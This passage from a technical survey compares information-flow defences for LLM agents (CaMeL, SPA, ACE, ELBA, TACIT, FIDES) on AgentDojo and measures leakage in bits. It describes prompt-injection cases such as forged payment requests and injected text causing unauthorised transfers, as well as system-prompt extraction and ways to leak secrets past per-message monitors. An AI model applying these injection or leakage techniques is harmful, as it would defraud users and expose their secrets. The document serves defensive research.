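| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 72.2% |
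| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 30.0% |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 41.5% |

With only 16 tasks, the 95% confidence intervals for the column without attacks extend about 20 points or more in each direction. CaMeL's figures under attack exclude the runs that did not complete.

Endorsement accounts for about 10 to 12 points of Randori's score without attacks. Three of the 16 tasks depend on it, because they ask the agent to act on the contents of an untrusted file. The planner writes the endorsements into its program before the agent reads any real data, so untrusted text cannot add one.

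Garby and colleagues conclude that Randori is secure with essentially no loss in completed tasks, whereas CaMeL's policies halve CaMeL's score. The comparison is not entirely fair to CaMeL, because Randori enforces looser policies. Randori's tool for sending money requires a trusted recipient but not a trusted amount, and its tool for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. Even without endorsement, Randori completed more tasks than CaMeL with policies on. That difference must come from the looser policies or other parts of the design, since LLMbda's rules for tracking labels are, if anything, stricter than CaMeL's.

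### What stopped the attacks

The attacker succeeded in two of Randori's 1,296 attacked runs. Both used GPT-5.2 with the same task and attack. The user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes, but the attacker has replaced the file with a different payment request. The planner endorsed the file's contents, as the task required. Without endorsement, both the attack and the task fail. No label can distinguish a genuine bill from a forged one in the same file. The CaMeL researchers treated the same case as outside the threats their system addresses.

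The other results are weaker evidence about the labels than they might seem. Garby and colleagues sorted the 144 combinations of task and attack by what would be needed to stop the attack. In 97, the attack requires a tool call that a program for the user's task would not contain, such as a payment when the user wants a summary of recent transactions. The planner writes its program before reading the injection, so the architecture alone should stop these attacks. In the other 47, a plausible program for the task could also carry out the attack, so the labels have to stop it.

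| Agent | Model | Stopped, where architecture should suffice | Stopped, where enforcement may be needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 291 of 291 | 139 of 141 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 98 of 99 | 141 of 141 |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 240 of 241 | 138 of 141 |

Even when CaMeL ran without policies, attacks succeeded in only three runs in the group where enforcement should matter, all with MiMo-v2.5. AgentDojo's fixed attacks therefore barely test the labels. A perfect score over 47 combinations is also consistent with a true resistance rate as low as 92.4%, so the main reason to trust LLMbda's enforcement is the theorem.

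The architecture failed once with each model. A user had asked CaMeL to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner could not see the file's contents, so it wrote a loop with a branch for every tool and used the contents to pick the branch. This let the attacker who wrote the file control the tool calls. With policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that completed.

### Where the guarantee ends

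The theorems treat tools as part of the program. In the banking study, each tool takes the account as a record and returns a changed version, and a layer of Python copies the final record back into AgentDojo. TIPNI therefore compares only what finished runs return. Like Smith's definition for ordinary programs, it does not cover visible calls that an agent with real tools makes before its run hangs. Covering real tools would require a definition that includes partial output, and the method of Hunt and colleagues is meant to allow this kind of extension.

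The guarantee also depends on correct labels where data enters the program. The published list of Randori's banking tools marks the contents of files as untrusted but does not give that label to the list of recent transactions. Anyone who sends the user money can write the transaction's subject line. If that text enters the program as trusted, the theorem still holds but offers no protection against the sender.

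If a plan contains no endorsements, even a completely compromised model can do only what the tools' checks allow. Once a plan includes endorsements, its integrity depends on the planner's judgement, and nothing in LLMbda prevents a planner from endorsing everything it reads. Developers can restrict endorsement to a small set of permitted values, which works for categories and yes-or-no answers. The banking tasks need account numbers and amounts, which have too many possible values to list, so the only justification for endorsing them is that the user told the agent to act on the file. Garby and colleagues suggest analysing plans before they run to enforce discipline in endorsements, but leave this to future work.

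## SPA, ACE and typed languages: checking a plan before it runs

If the model writes a complete plan before the agent reads any data, ordinary code can analyse the plan and refuse to run it. The model is still unpredictable, but the checker only has to analyse a finished plan, as a compiler analyses a program under Denning and Denning's certification method. Because the checker examines every branch, it can also catch leaks through skipped branches, which CaMeL's run-time labels missed. But it also has to reject a plan for what a branch might do, even if that branch would never have run.

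### SPA's planning language

*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) applies this approach to an agent that keeps results from one request to the next. For each request, a model writes one plan, using only the request, the list of tools, a record of earlier requests and short descriptions of stored results. A checker accepts or rejects the whole plan before any tool runs. If the plan is accepted, an interpreter follows it exactly, and the model never sees what the tools return.

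A plan can contain six kinds of step. In the table, pc is the program-counter label, which starts as the label of the user's request. A step's *input label* is the join of pc and the labels of the variables the step uses.

| Step | What it does | Label rule |
|---|---|---|
| `retrieve` | loads a stored result | the result gets its stored label ⊔ pc |
| `tool` | calls a tool | the tool's policy must allow the input label; the result gets the input label ⊔ the tool's output label |
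| `q-llm` | has a quarantined model extract values from text | the result gets the input label |
| `condition` | runs one of two branches | both branches must pass with pc ⊔ the labels of the tested values |
| `loop` | repeats some steps for each item in a list | the steps must pass with pc ⊔ the list's label, and each item gets that label |
| `display` | shows text to the user | a marker replaces any item that the display's policy does not allow |

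A tool needs its own output label because its arguments do not always determine how sensitive its result is. For example, a mailbox search for a public word still returns secret, untrusted text.

The language leaves out most of what makes programs hard to analyse. A plan cannot do arithmetic or insert values into strings, so every use of data appears as a variable name. A plan can assign each variable only once, and a variable created inside a branch or loop disappears when that branch or loop ends. This prevents a planner from setting a default and overriding it in a branch, the pattern that leaked information in CaMeL. Variables also cannot carry values from one round of a loop to the next, so the checker needs to go through the loop only once.

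### One plan, accepted and then rejected

Suppose a user asks an agent to save a summary of Friday's medical appointment in a private notebook and to tell the office about the absence. In simplified notation, the plan is:

```
record  = tool read_record(day="Friday")
summary = q-llm("Summarize the appointment", record)
tool save_private_note(text=summary)
tool send_email(to="office@example.com", body="I am away on Friday.")
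```

The request is trusted and public, and so are the constants that the planner writes. Medical records are trusted and secret.

| Step | Input label | What the tool accepts | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_record` | trusted, public | trusted data, public or secret | passes |
| `q-llm` | trusted, secret | anything | passes |
| `save_private_note` | trusted, secret | trusted data, public or secret | passes |
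| `send_email` | trusted, public | trusted data, public only | passes |

The checker accepts this plan. Now suppose the user wants the email to go out only if the appointment is with an oncologist, so the planner replaces the last line:

```
condition record.department == "oncology":
    tool send_email(to="office@example.com", body="I am away on Friday.")
```

The tested value is secret, so pc is secret inside the branch and the input label of `send_email` becomes trusted and secret. The email tool accepts only public data, so the checker rejects the whole plan, even though the message contains nothing from the record. The checker does this before any tool runs and without reading the record, so it would reject the plan whatever department the record listed.

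### What an accepted plan guarantees

Girrens and Wang define which plans pass, but they do not state or prove a noninterference theorem. One could be stated for an observer who sees only calls to tools that accept only public data. In an accepted plan, each of these calls has a public input label, so its arguments come only from public values and it is not inside a branch or loop that depends on a secret. Two runs that differ only in secrets therefore make the same public calls for as long as both continue. This argument assumes that every tool's output label is correct and that the quarantined model always gives the same answer to the same input.

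SPA ends a request when a tool fails, a field is missing or a value has the wrong format, and a secret can cause any of these. The guarantee would therefore be termination-insensitive noninterference as Askarov and colleagues define it, which allows a secret to cut short the sequence of public calls.

The argument does not extend to `display`. If the display's policy forbids an item, the checker puts a redaction marker in its place and still accepts the plan. When the `display` step is inside a branch that depends on a secret, the marker appears only if that branch runs. In a loop over a secret list, the marker appears once per item, so a reader could count the items. This is a leak whenever the reader is not allowed to know the secret. Rejecting the plan, as SPA does for tools, would prevent it.

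### Results kept for later requests

Girrens and Wang give the example of a user who asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and keep its details. An attacker has put a different account number in the invoice. On Tuesday the user asks the agent to pay the invoice.

SPA stores the invoice with its untrusted label. Tuesday's planner receives only a description of the data's format and meaning. Monday's planner wrote that description before the invoice arrived, so it contains none of the attacker's text. When Tuesday's plan retrieves the invoice, the untrusted label comes with it, and the checker rejects the payment. The checker would also reject payment of a genuine invoice, because SPA has no way to endorse data.

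In SPA, the planner's input still depends on whether earlier requests succeeded, because SPA saves results only after a request succeeds. If a stranger's file makes Monday's request fail, the invoice will be missing from Tuesday's list, and the planner may write a different plan. f-secure has a similar leak through failed steps. SPA could avoid its leak by listing every result that a plan was supposed to produce, even if the request fails, since the descriptions come from the plan and not from the data.

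### Whether a rejection can leak

When CaMeL refuses a call, the refusal can reveal a secret because it may depend on which branch ran. SPA's verdict depends on less:

```
plan     =  planner(request, tool list, descriptions of stored results)
verdict  =  check(plan, labels of stored results, policies)
```

If all the inputs in brackets are trusted and public, two runs that differ only in secrets and untrusted text have the same distribution of plans, as in the proof for f-secure. The verdict is a fixed function of the plan and other inputs that are the same in both runs. A rejection is therefore equally likely in each run, so it reveals nothing about the secrets, and an attacker's text cannot cause it.

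The labels of stored results meet this condition because they come from earlier checks, not from the data. The list of stored results does not fully meet it, because the list depends on which requests succeeded. If the request is secret, the verdict may depend on it. But pc then starts out secret, so an accepted plan can make no public calls, and someone who sees only public calls sees none whether the plan is accepted or rejected.

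SPA could tell the planner why the checker rejected a plan and still preserve noninterference, because the explanation would depend only on the same trusted, public inputs. Instead, SPA gives the planner one attempt and no explanation, so that it cannot keep revising an unsafe plan until it passes. But a revised plan would still have to pass every rule, so the limit of one attempt mainly helps if the checker has gaps that a planner could find by trial and error.

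### What the check costs

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo with GPT-5.4 nano, a small OpenAI model. They also split each task into two to five successive requests to test how the agent reuses stored results.

| Test | Label check | Tasks completed, no attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single requests | off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Single requests | on | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Successive requests | off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
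| Successive requests | on | 35.3% | 0.2% |

On single requests, the checker rejected about 53% of plans, usually because they passed untrusted tool output to a tool that requires trusted input. The loss ranged from 6 percentage points in banking to 35 in travel.

Even without the check, only four of 949 attacks on single requests succeeded, so writing the plan in advance already stopped almost all of them. The check stopped the other four, which all targeted the same banking task. In these, injected text passed through the quarantined model and led to three unauthorised transfers and a changed password. The 0.2% in the last row is two runs, and the checker had rejected the plan in both, so they appear to be scoring errors. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that AgentDojo's attacks were not designed to wait in storage for a later request, so the successive tests are weak evidence about such attacks.

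Hiding stored values from the planner reduced task completion much less than the label check did. When the planner could read the values and the check was off, it completed 65.9% of the successive tasks, compared with 62.5% when it saw only descriptions.

### Three other designs

*ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, NDSS security conference, 2026) checks plans for assistants that use third-party apps. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents ELBA, in which the model writes Haskell. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, in which the model writes Scala 3. Both languages have type systems that can restrict what a program does. In TACIT, the types track *capabilities*, which are objects that give code permission to use a resource such as a file or a network connection.

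| System | What it checks before the run | Property | Can the model read untrusted results between steps? |
|---|---|---|---|
| SPA | labels throughout the plan | aims at noninterference, without a theorem | no |
| ACE | labels throughout the plan | aims at noninterference, without a theorem | no |
| ELBA | which operations the code uses | whatever the chosen library enforces, which can include label checks during the run | yes |
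| TACIT | which capabilities the code uses | capability control, and secrecy for data in a special wrapper | yes, unless the data is in the wrapper |

### ACE: plans for apps that may be malicious

A malicious app can use its description to attack an assistant, for example by telling the planner to ignore a competing app. ACE's planner therefore receives only the user's request and trusted background information. It invents the apps it needs, such as a file reader, and writes a program in restricted Python that calls them. Another model then matches each invented app to installed ones. It evaluates each pair separately, so one app's description cannot exclude another app.

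The checker converts the program into a list of flows. Li and colleagues give this example:

```
a = SecretInfo()
b = ""
if a[0] == "0":
    b += "0"
else:
    b += "1"
```

The list includes a flow from the condition to `b` for each branch, so `b` becomes secret whichever branch runs. Loops are harder to check because ACE, unlike SPA, lets a variable change between rounds. If a loop sends `a` over the network and then loads bank details into `a`, the first round is harmless but the second sends the bank details. ACE catches this leak by repeating its analysis until the labels stop changing.

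Li and colleagues state that they cannot guarantee the check is sound, because Python's behaviour is too complex, and they leave a noninterference proof to future work. Their description suggests a possible gap. The checker takes a branch's condition into account when it labels the steps inside that branch, but one of their published plans ends the program from inside a branch. Whether the later steps run then also depends on the condition, and the rule as described does not reflect this in their labels. A plan that stopped early for one value of a secret and otherwise sent a public email could pass the check.

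ACE never ran the attacker's app when tested against the attacks in InjecAgent, the benchmark Wu and colleagues used to test f-secure. On three sets of tool-use tasks, ACE with GPT-4.1 got 80% to 95% of final results right, taking 12 to 21 seconds and costing up to $0.27 per request. These scores do not measure how many useful plans the label check rejects. Girrens and Wang tried ACE's kind of planning as an option in SPA, but about three quarters of runs in this mode failed because the system could not match an invented tool to a real one. SPA completed only 14.1% of AgentDojo tasks this way, and 6.7% with the label check on.

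### ELBA: types before the run, labels during it

A Haskell type records which side effects a program may have. In ELBA, a developer states what type of program the agent must return, and the type checker rejects anything else. If the required type is a plain integer, the model can write code that computes a number but not code that deletes a file. When a program fails the check, the model receives the error and tries again. On AgentDojo this happened 0.13 times per run on average.

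For information flow, Zhou and colleagues use an existing Haskell library called LIO. It keeps a single label covering everything the running computation has read and blocks writes that this label forbids. The type checker only ensures that the program goes through LIO. A program that reads an untrusted web page and then writes to a place that requires trusted data therefore passes the type check but fails when it runs. Such a failure can depend on a secret, but ELBA retries only after type errors, which occur before the program has called any tools.

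ELBA's programs can call the model again with data they have just read. LIO can run such a call separately and seal its result, as `fork` does in LLMbda. Unlike a quarantined model, the new call may use any tools its label still allows.

Zhou and colleagues prove that any property Haskell's types guarantee for ordinary programs also holds for programs that call an agent. The proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that obtains the model's code, checks its type and runs it. The property may concern a program's whole set of traces, as noninterference does, so the theorem could in principle extend noninterference to programs that call an agent. But it assumes that the model always gives the same reply to the same prompt, so it does not cover probabilistic noninterference. Some tools also make deliberate exceptions to noninterference, such as a messaging tool that accepts a message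 body influenced by untrusted data.

In the first version of the paper, ELBA with GPT-5.4 completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with policies off and 8 with policies on. A revised version tested four models:

| Model | ELBA, policies off | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
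| GPT-5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |

Zhou and colleagues attribute the losses to tasks that no secure policy would allow, such as forwarding the contents of an untrusted channel. AgentDojo's attacks all failed even with policies off. In a separate adversarial test, ELBA resisted all injections with policies on and between 57.8% and 84.5% with them off, depending on the model. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL because it calls the model again as new data arrives.

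### TACIT: secrets that code can use but not reveal

Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, records in a function's type which capabilities the function uses. A function that takes a string and writes it to file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, while the plain arrow in `String -> Int` means the function uses no capabilities. *LACUNA* (2026) describes another agent system based on this feature, in which generated code cannot use a capability that is not available where the code is inserted.

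TACIT puts secrets in a wrapper called `Classified`. Its `map` operation applies a function to the contents, but only if the function uses no capabilities:

```
secret.map(text => text.length)         accepted, and the length stays wrapped
secret.map(text => file.write(text))    rejected before it runs
```

Printing a wrapped value shows its real contents on the user's terminal but adds only `Classified(****)` to the model's conversation. Code inside `map` may branch on the secret because that code cannot affect anything outside `map` and its result stays wrapped. Two runs with different secrets therefore give the model the same conversation, for the same reason as in f-secure.

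Odersky and colleagues claim noninterference for these functions, but the computer-checked proofs cover only Scala's basic capture checking, not the restricted "safe mode" in which TACIT compiles agents' code. The claim also excludes leaks through timing and termination. This is a serious limit for TACIT because the model may itself be the attacker and can keep submitting code. It could extract a secret one bit at a time with the kind of loop Birgisson and Sabelfeld describe.

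TACIT's only protection against untrusted text is capability control. The model reads ordinary web pages and tool results directly, and an injection can make it do anything its capabilities allow. If an agent has permission to post on a website, an attacker could make it post any unwrapped text.

Odersky and colleagues tested Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5 on a software project with a folder of secrets. With the wrapper, neither model leaked anything in 131 trials. Without it, secrets appeared in the output in 1.5% of trials with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 8.4% with MiniMax M2.5.

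Writing Scala did not make the models much worse at ordinary work. Three models did 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points better on simulated customer-service tasks than with normal tool calls, and MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% of a set of real software bugs, compared with 43.3% without Scala. The AgentDojo results are more mixed than the paper suggests when it calls them comparable to CaMeL's. TACIT completed 52.9% of office tasks with o4-mini, compared with 81.4% for CaMeL, but it completed 64.3% of travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, compared with 1.4% for CaMeL.

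## Small answers: counting the bits an agent may leak

f-secure does not let even a yes or no from its quarantined model influence the plan, but other designs do. Each such exception breaks noninterference, and the usual defence is that a yes or no cannot carry much. *Quantitative information flow* puts a number on this by measuring how much an observer learns about a secret from a program's output. For integrity, the attacker's text takes the place of the secret, and the number limits how much of that text can reach the planner.

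### Three measures of a leak

Let X be the secret, Y the output, and p(x) the publicly known probability of each secret x. The Shannon entropy H(X) = Σ p(x) log₂(1/p(x)) is the observer's average uncertainty in bits. The vulnerability V(X) is the largest p(x), which is the chance that the best single guess is right. H(X given Y) and V(X given Y) are the same quantities calculated after the observer has seen the output, averaged over the possible outputs.

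| Measure | Formula | Question it answers |
|---|---|---|
| Shannon leakage | H(X) − H(X given Y) | How far does the output reduce average uncertainty? |
| Min-entropy leakage | log₂( V(X given Y) / V(X) ) | How much does the output improve a single guess at the whole secret? |
| Channel capacity | the largest Shannon leakage over all choices of p | How much could the program leak on average, however likely each secret is? |

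Under noninterference, all three measures are zero, but min-entropy leakage can also be zero when noninterference is violated. For example, if 95% of patients are healthy and an output raises one patient's chance of illness from 5% to 20%, the output reveals information about that patient, but "healthy" is still the best guess.

In 2009, Smith, in *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow*, argued that Shannon leakage, then the standard choice, says little about the risk of a correct guess. Take a 64-bit secret with all values equally likely. Program A reveals the whole secret one time in eight:

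```
A:  if secret % 8 == 0: output(secret)
    else:               output(1)

B:  output(secret % 512)
```

| | Program A | Program B |
|---|---|---|
| Shannon leakage | 8.17 bits | 9 bits |
| Uncertainty left | 55.83 bits | 55 bits |
| Chance of guessing the secret | about 1 in 8 | 1 in 2⁵⁵ |
| Min-entropy leakage | about 61 bits | 9 bits |

Program B is worse than program A when measured by Shannon leakage. One in eight runs of A reveals all 64 bits, but the measure averages that run with seven that reveal almost nothing. A quarantined model that usually writes a harmless summary but occasionally quotes a password would look similarly safe on average.

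### The bound for n possible answers

If the output can take only n values, none of the three measures can exceed log₂ n. For min-entropy leakage, this follows from Smith's formula for vulnerability:

```
V(X given Y)  =  Σ_y max_x p(x) · p(y given x)
              ≤  Σ_y max_x p(x)  =  n × V(X)
```

A yes-or-no answer at most doubles the chance of guessing a secret correctly, and a choice of eight tags multiplies it by at most eight, a leak of at most 3 bits. LLMbda's theorem allows a factor of two for the same reason, because a run that does not finish is one extra outcome. The bound holds for any model, including one that samples its replies or obeys an attacker, and it requires no estimate of how strongly a text influenced the model. Program A has more than 2⁶¹ possible outputs, so its bound is more than 61 bits.

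### Output types in FIDES labels

In FIDES, the planner can tell the quarantined model what type of answer to return. *Constrained decoding* enforces the type by preventing the model from generating text that does not fit it. Costa and colleagues add the type to the answer's label and order types by how much they can carry:

```
bool  ⊑  enum["a", "b", "c"]  ⊑  string
```

A policy can then let a consequential call depend on an untrusted `bool` but not on an untrusted `string`. In the calendar example, the planner inspects only a yes or no on whether an email requests a meeting. The quarantined model then extracts the details into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool. The single bit limits a stranger's influence on whether the agent creates an event, but the stranger's email still determines what the event says and whom it invites.

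Type labels also do not record how many answers a context contains. The join of `bool` and `bool` is `bool`, so a context with fifty inspected answers has the same type label as a context with one. A policy that accepts `bool` because each answer carries at most one bit could therefore allow a leak of up to fifty bits. The AgentDojo results for FIDES do not test any of this, because Costa and colleagues left out constrained decoding, which they found unnecessary for most of the tasks.

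### A fixed list in LLMbda

Garby and colleagues get a similar effect with a wrapper around LLMbda's `endorse`. In simplified notation:

```
bounded_endorse(v):
    allowed = ["general", "billing", "complaint"]
    w = endorse(v)
    if w in allowed: return w        # trusted
    else:            return v        # still untrusted
```

The wrapper has to endorse the value before testing it. If it tested the untrusted `v` first, the program-counter label inside the branch would become untrusted and the endorsement would have no effect. The list must also be fixed in advance, and code that the model writes must have access only to the wrapper, not to `endorse`.

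Garby and colleagues put the limit on the leak at log₂ n bits when the reply must come from a list of n values, and they leave a formal proof to future work. A strict count gives log₂(n + 1), because a rejected reply is one more possible outcome, which trusted code can detect by testing the label of the result. Seven permitted tags and a rejection therefore allow a leak of 3 bits, the same as eight tags when the model must choose one.

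### Fifty emails

Suppose a quarantined model sorts each incoming email into one of eight categories, and the agent's automatic reply shows the category. Each reply carries up to 3 bits. Over 50 emails there are 8⁵⁰ = 2¹⁵⁰ possible sequences of categories, so 50 replies can carry up to 150 bits. If the model can also read a file containing a 128-bit encryption key, 43 replies could carry the whole key.

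The same count applies to integrity. A stranger who writes all 50 emails can choose among 2¹⁵⁰ sequences of tags for the planner to read. Those 150 bits could encode about 19 characters of plain text, but a planner that sees only category names is unlikely to treat them as an instruction.

These totals are upper limits, and the actual leak depends on the questions. Smith compares two yes-or-no tests, one checking whether a secret equals a given number and the other whether it is at most that number. Fifty equality tests can separate the secrets into only 51 groups, which is less than 6 bits, while fifty well-chosen comparisons can separate them into 2⁵⁰ groups, or 50 bits. *Quantitative Information Flow under Generic Leakage Functions and Adaptive Adversaries* shows how to compute an attacker's best sequence of questions by working backwards from the last one.

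### When the bits add up

Counts of possible answers can always be multiplied across questions, even if the attacker chooses each question after seeing the previous answers. Average leakage can't always be bounded so simply. *Bits Leaked per Query* (Kaneko and Baldwin, 2025) states that N adaptive queries leak at most N times the maximum leakage of a single query. Its proof uses the maximum from before the attacker has learned anything, and a small example shows why this fails.

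Suppose the secret is one of 4,096 files, spread evenly over four folders. The attacker may ask which folder contains the file, or may name a folder and ask which file it is, getting "no" if the folder is wrong. An attacker who asks for the folder and then for the file in that folder learns all 12 bits. Asked first, the folder question leaks 2 bits and the file question leaks 3.3 bits on average, so doubling the larger figure gives a limit of 6.6 bits for two queries, which is too low. Counting answers gives the right limit, since the 4 × 1,025 possible pairs of answers come to just over 12 bits.

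Monitoring each message separately has a related flaw. In *Don't Judge an Agent by Its Messages*, Pandey, Duttagupta and colleagues (2026) consider a monitor that can measure only how often each message occurs. If a sender uses one message two thirds of the time and another the remaining third, a single message can reveal up to 0.459 bits about a secret coin flip. Two messages can reveal up to 1.099 bits about two flips, more than twice as much.

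Whether the total carries over between sessions depends on what persists. If the agent can still access the same key, every session adds to the leak. If the user replaces the key, earlier answers don't help anyone guess the new one. For integrity, the count can restart only if the planner starts without any earlier answers, including those in stored results or long-term memory.

### What a budget would have to count

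A leakage budget sets in advance the total number of bits an agent may leak, and makes the agent stop or ask its user when the budget runs out. *Trident* has such a budget for signals of success and failure. The number of bits deducted should depend on the type of question and not on the answer, because otherwise when the budget runs out would reveal something about the answers.

To cover everything an observer sees, a budget has to limit the number of different traces that observer could see:

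```
total leak  ≤  log₂(number of distinguishable traces)
```

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) counts a refusal as one more outcome, so a call that may use any of d permitted capabilities carries at most log₂(d + 1) bits. With ten capabilities and eight calls, there are 11⁸ possible traces, so a trace carries at most just under 28 bits. This figure covers only which capability each call uses. If one capability is sending email, the text of a single message can carry far more, so the budget must also count the arguments passed to each call.

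An agent can leak information through the order of its calls even when every argument is fixed. Ten prepared messages can be sent in 3,628,800 different orders, so the order alone can carry almost 22 bits. If a secret also determines whether the planner asks a yes-or-no question or asks for one of eight tags, an observer who sees the question learns something about the secret before the answer arrives.

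Agents that delegate work need a shared budget; otherwise, each new agent would bring a fresh allowance. Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026), in *L3M*, solve this for spending, in a runtime where agents lend part of their budget to the agents they create. They prove that, for one batch of loans, a tree of agents cannot spend more than its root was given. They also outline, but have not implemented, a leakage budget that would meter every connection and cap each leak at the smaller of what the sender holds and what it sends.

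A narrower interface makes any leakage budget last longer. Pandey and colleagues replaced one agent's free-text messages with a choice among 16 routes. They found that this left the receiving agent's decisions unchanged and limited the leak about an unrelated private bit to 0.028 bits.

### When one bit matters more than a thousand

A bit that approves a payment can do more damage than a thousand bits that choose the wording of a greeting, and none of the three measures reflects this. For secrecy, one remedy is *g-leakage*, which Chatzikokolakis, Alvim and colleagues (2013), in *Measuring Information Leakage using Gain Functions*, present. It replaces the chance of a correct guess with the attacker's expected gain. Let g(w, x) be what the attacker gains from taking action w when the secret is x:

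```
V_g(X)          =  max_w Σ_x p(x) · g(w, x)
V_g(X given Y)  =  Σ_y max_w Σ_x p(x) · p(y given x) · g(w, x)
g-leakage       =  log₂( V_g(X given Y) / V_g(X) )
```

If w is a guess at the secret, and g is 1 when the guess is right and 0 otherwise, this is min-entropy leakage. Other choices of g separate leaks that min-entropy leakage treats as equal. Suppose a record contains a diagnosis, equally likely to be positive or negative, and an independent 10-bit locker code:

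| The output reveals | Min-entropy leakage | g-leakage if the attacker wants the diagnosis | g-leakage if the attacker wants to open the locker |
|---|---|---|---|
| the diagnosis | 1 bit | 1 bit | 0 |
| the first bit of the code | 1 bit | 0 | 1 bit |

The earlier derivation still works as long as gains are never negative, so n possible answers multiply the expected gain by at most n. A defender who limits the number of answers therefore gets some protection without knowing what the attacker wants. But the limit is relative to what the attacker already expects to gain, so if that is $50,000, one bit may add another $50,000.

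g-leakage measures what someone learns from an output, whereas an attack on integrity is about what someone makes the agent do. The idea of weighing outcomes still applies. Give each permitted answer a harm, h, equal to the damage that would follow if the attacker chose that answer:

```
worst harm of one answer  =  max h(a)   over all permitted answers a
worst harm of a run       ≤  the sum of these maxima, if harms add up
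```

Reducing the number of possible answers does not by itself limit the harm an attacker can do. Cutting a list of a hundred answers to two won't stop a fraudulent payment if "approve the payment" is one of the two. Restricting the payment tool does limit the harm. If the agent may approve at most ten invoices a day without asking the user, each under $50, the user will lose less than $500 a day even if an attacker controls every answer.

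Someone still has to choose the harms, which depend on what happens after the call. A 1,000-bit greeting, about 125 characters, is nearly harmless if a person reads it, but it is long enough to contain a prompt injection if another agent reads it.

### What attackers recover in practice

Kaneko and Baldwin tested how leakage affects the number of queries an attack needs, using seven language models without tools. The attacks tried to extract a hidden system prompt, obtain harmful output, or recover text that the model had been trained to forget. The researchers estimated I, the average number of bits that one reply revealed about the attacker's target, and counted the queries needed to succeed. Attackers needed about a thousand queries when they saw only the model's answers, about a hundred when they also saw its numerical scores for possible words, and a few dozen when they saw its written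 reasoning.

The number of queries was close to inversely proportional to I for attacks that adapted to earlier replies, as Kaneko and Baldwin had predicted, but not for attacks that only paraphrased a fixed request. The researchers also present log₂(1/ε)/I as the minimum number of queries for a failure rate of ε. This cannot hold in general, because one query is enough for any ε if the reply reveals a yes-or-no fact outright.

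In *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage*, Huang, Wu and colleagues (2026) measured leaks through several parts of an agent. They sent 30 attack queries to each test system, repeated this with five random seeds, and used five models, including GPT-4o and DeepSeek. The table shows, as ranges across the models, how often a query exposed at least one of the private items the agent had retrieved and how often it exposed all of them.

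| Where the attacker looks | At least one item | Every retrieved item |
|---|---|---|
| Output of agents with a memory of past records | 100% | 100% |
| Answers based on retrieved documents | 80–98% | 0–21% |
| Arguments of tool calls | 27–100% | 26–100% |
| Tool results repeated to the user | 37–100% | 36–100% |

Removing the explicit requests for private data from the prompts for the two tool channels cut the rate to 6.7% or less for every model. The high figures therefore apply to deliberate attacks, not ordinary use. The retrieval and tool systems were also small, with five private items each.

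These rates count items, which can differ greatly in size. Naming one of five documents reveals at most 2.3 bits, while quoting a document can reveal thousands. Exact matching also misses paraphrases. When Huang and colleagues read 200 of the outputs themselves, they found 12 that disclosed private information although the automatic check had found nothing in them.

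## Estimated influence: dropping labels the model seems not to have used

Giving each reply the join of all the labels in the conversation is sound, but it soon marks everything an agent writes as untrusted and secret. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls label propagation through models an open problem and the join the only safe assumption currently available. Several systems instead estimate which inputs a reply used and drop the labels of the rest.

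The benefit of dropping labels depends on the task. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) studied model calls in open-source programs that fill a prompt template with values such as a query or a retrieved document. Only 12% to 14% of the values had no visible effect on the output, so the join of their labels was usually right. An agent with a long history of tool results probably has more labels to drop.

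### Answering again from fewer documents

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, propose a wrapper for a model that answers questions from labelled documents:

1. The model answers from all the documents.
2. The wrapper tries less strict labels. For each one, it keeps only the documents that may flow to that label and calculates how likely the model would be to write the same answer from them.
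3. If the answer remains almost as likely, within a set tolerance, the model writes a new answer from the remaining documents.
4. The wrapper returns the new answer with the less strict label and discards the original.

Suppose a web search for the population of New York returns a trusted page that gives 8.4 million and an untrusted one that gives 8 million. The trusted page is enough to produce the answer "8.4 million", so the wrapper can return that answer as trusted.

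Returning a new answer is safer than relabelling the old one. If the wrapper wrongly classifies a document as irrelevant, the new answer still contains nothing from it, because the model wrote that answer without the document. This holds even if the document contains an injection.

Siddiqui and colleagues measured how often the wrapper finds the right label, using Llama 2 models with 7 and 70 billion parameters. On 64 questions about personal records, with 14 documents each, it found exactly the right labels 86% of the time. Asking the model which documents it had used worked in at most 13% of cases. On news articles, 647 of 3,465 questions allowed a less strict label. The wrapper found that label for 57% of the 647 with the small model and 39% with the large one. In 20 agent conversations where the label could improve, it succeeded in 17 with one model and 19 with the other. In another 20,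 the answer needed an untrusted document, and leaving that document out lowered the answer's overlap with the correct one by about 0.3 on a scale from 0 to 1.

Costa and colleagues note that FIDES could use this method, but they left it out for simplicity.

### How the choice of label can leak

The guarantee covers the text of the answer but not the decision to return it with a less strict label. Suppose a journalist asks a company's agent when a product will launch. A public announcement gives 3 May, and a secret memo either confirms the date or moves it to June.

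| | Memo confirms 3 May | Memo says June |
|---|---|---|
| Answer from both documents | 3 May | June |
| Likely from the announcement alone? | yes | no |
| Label of the returned answer | public | secret |
| Reply to the journalist | "3 May" | blocked |

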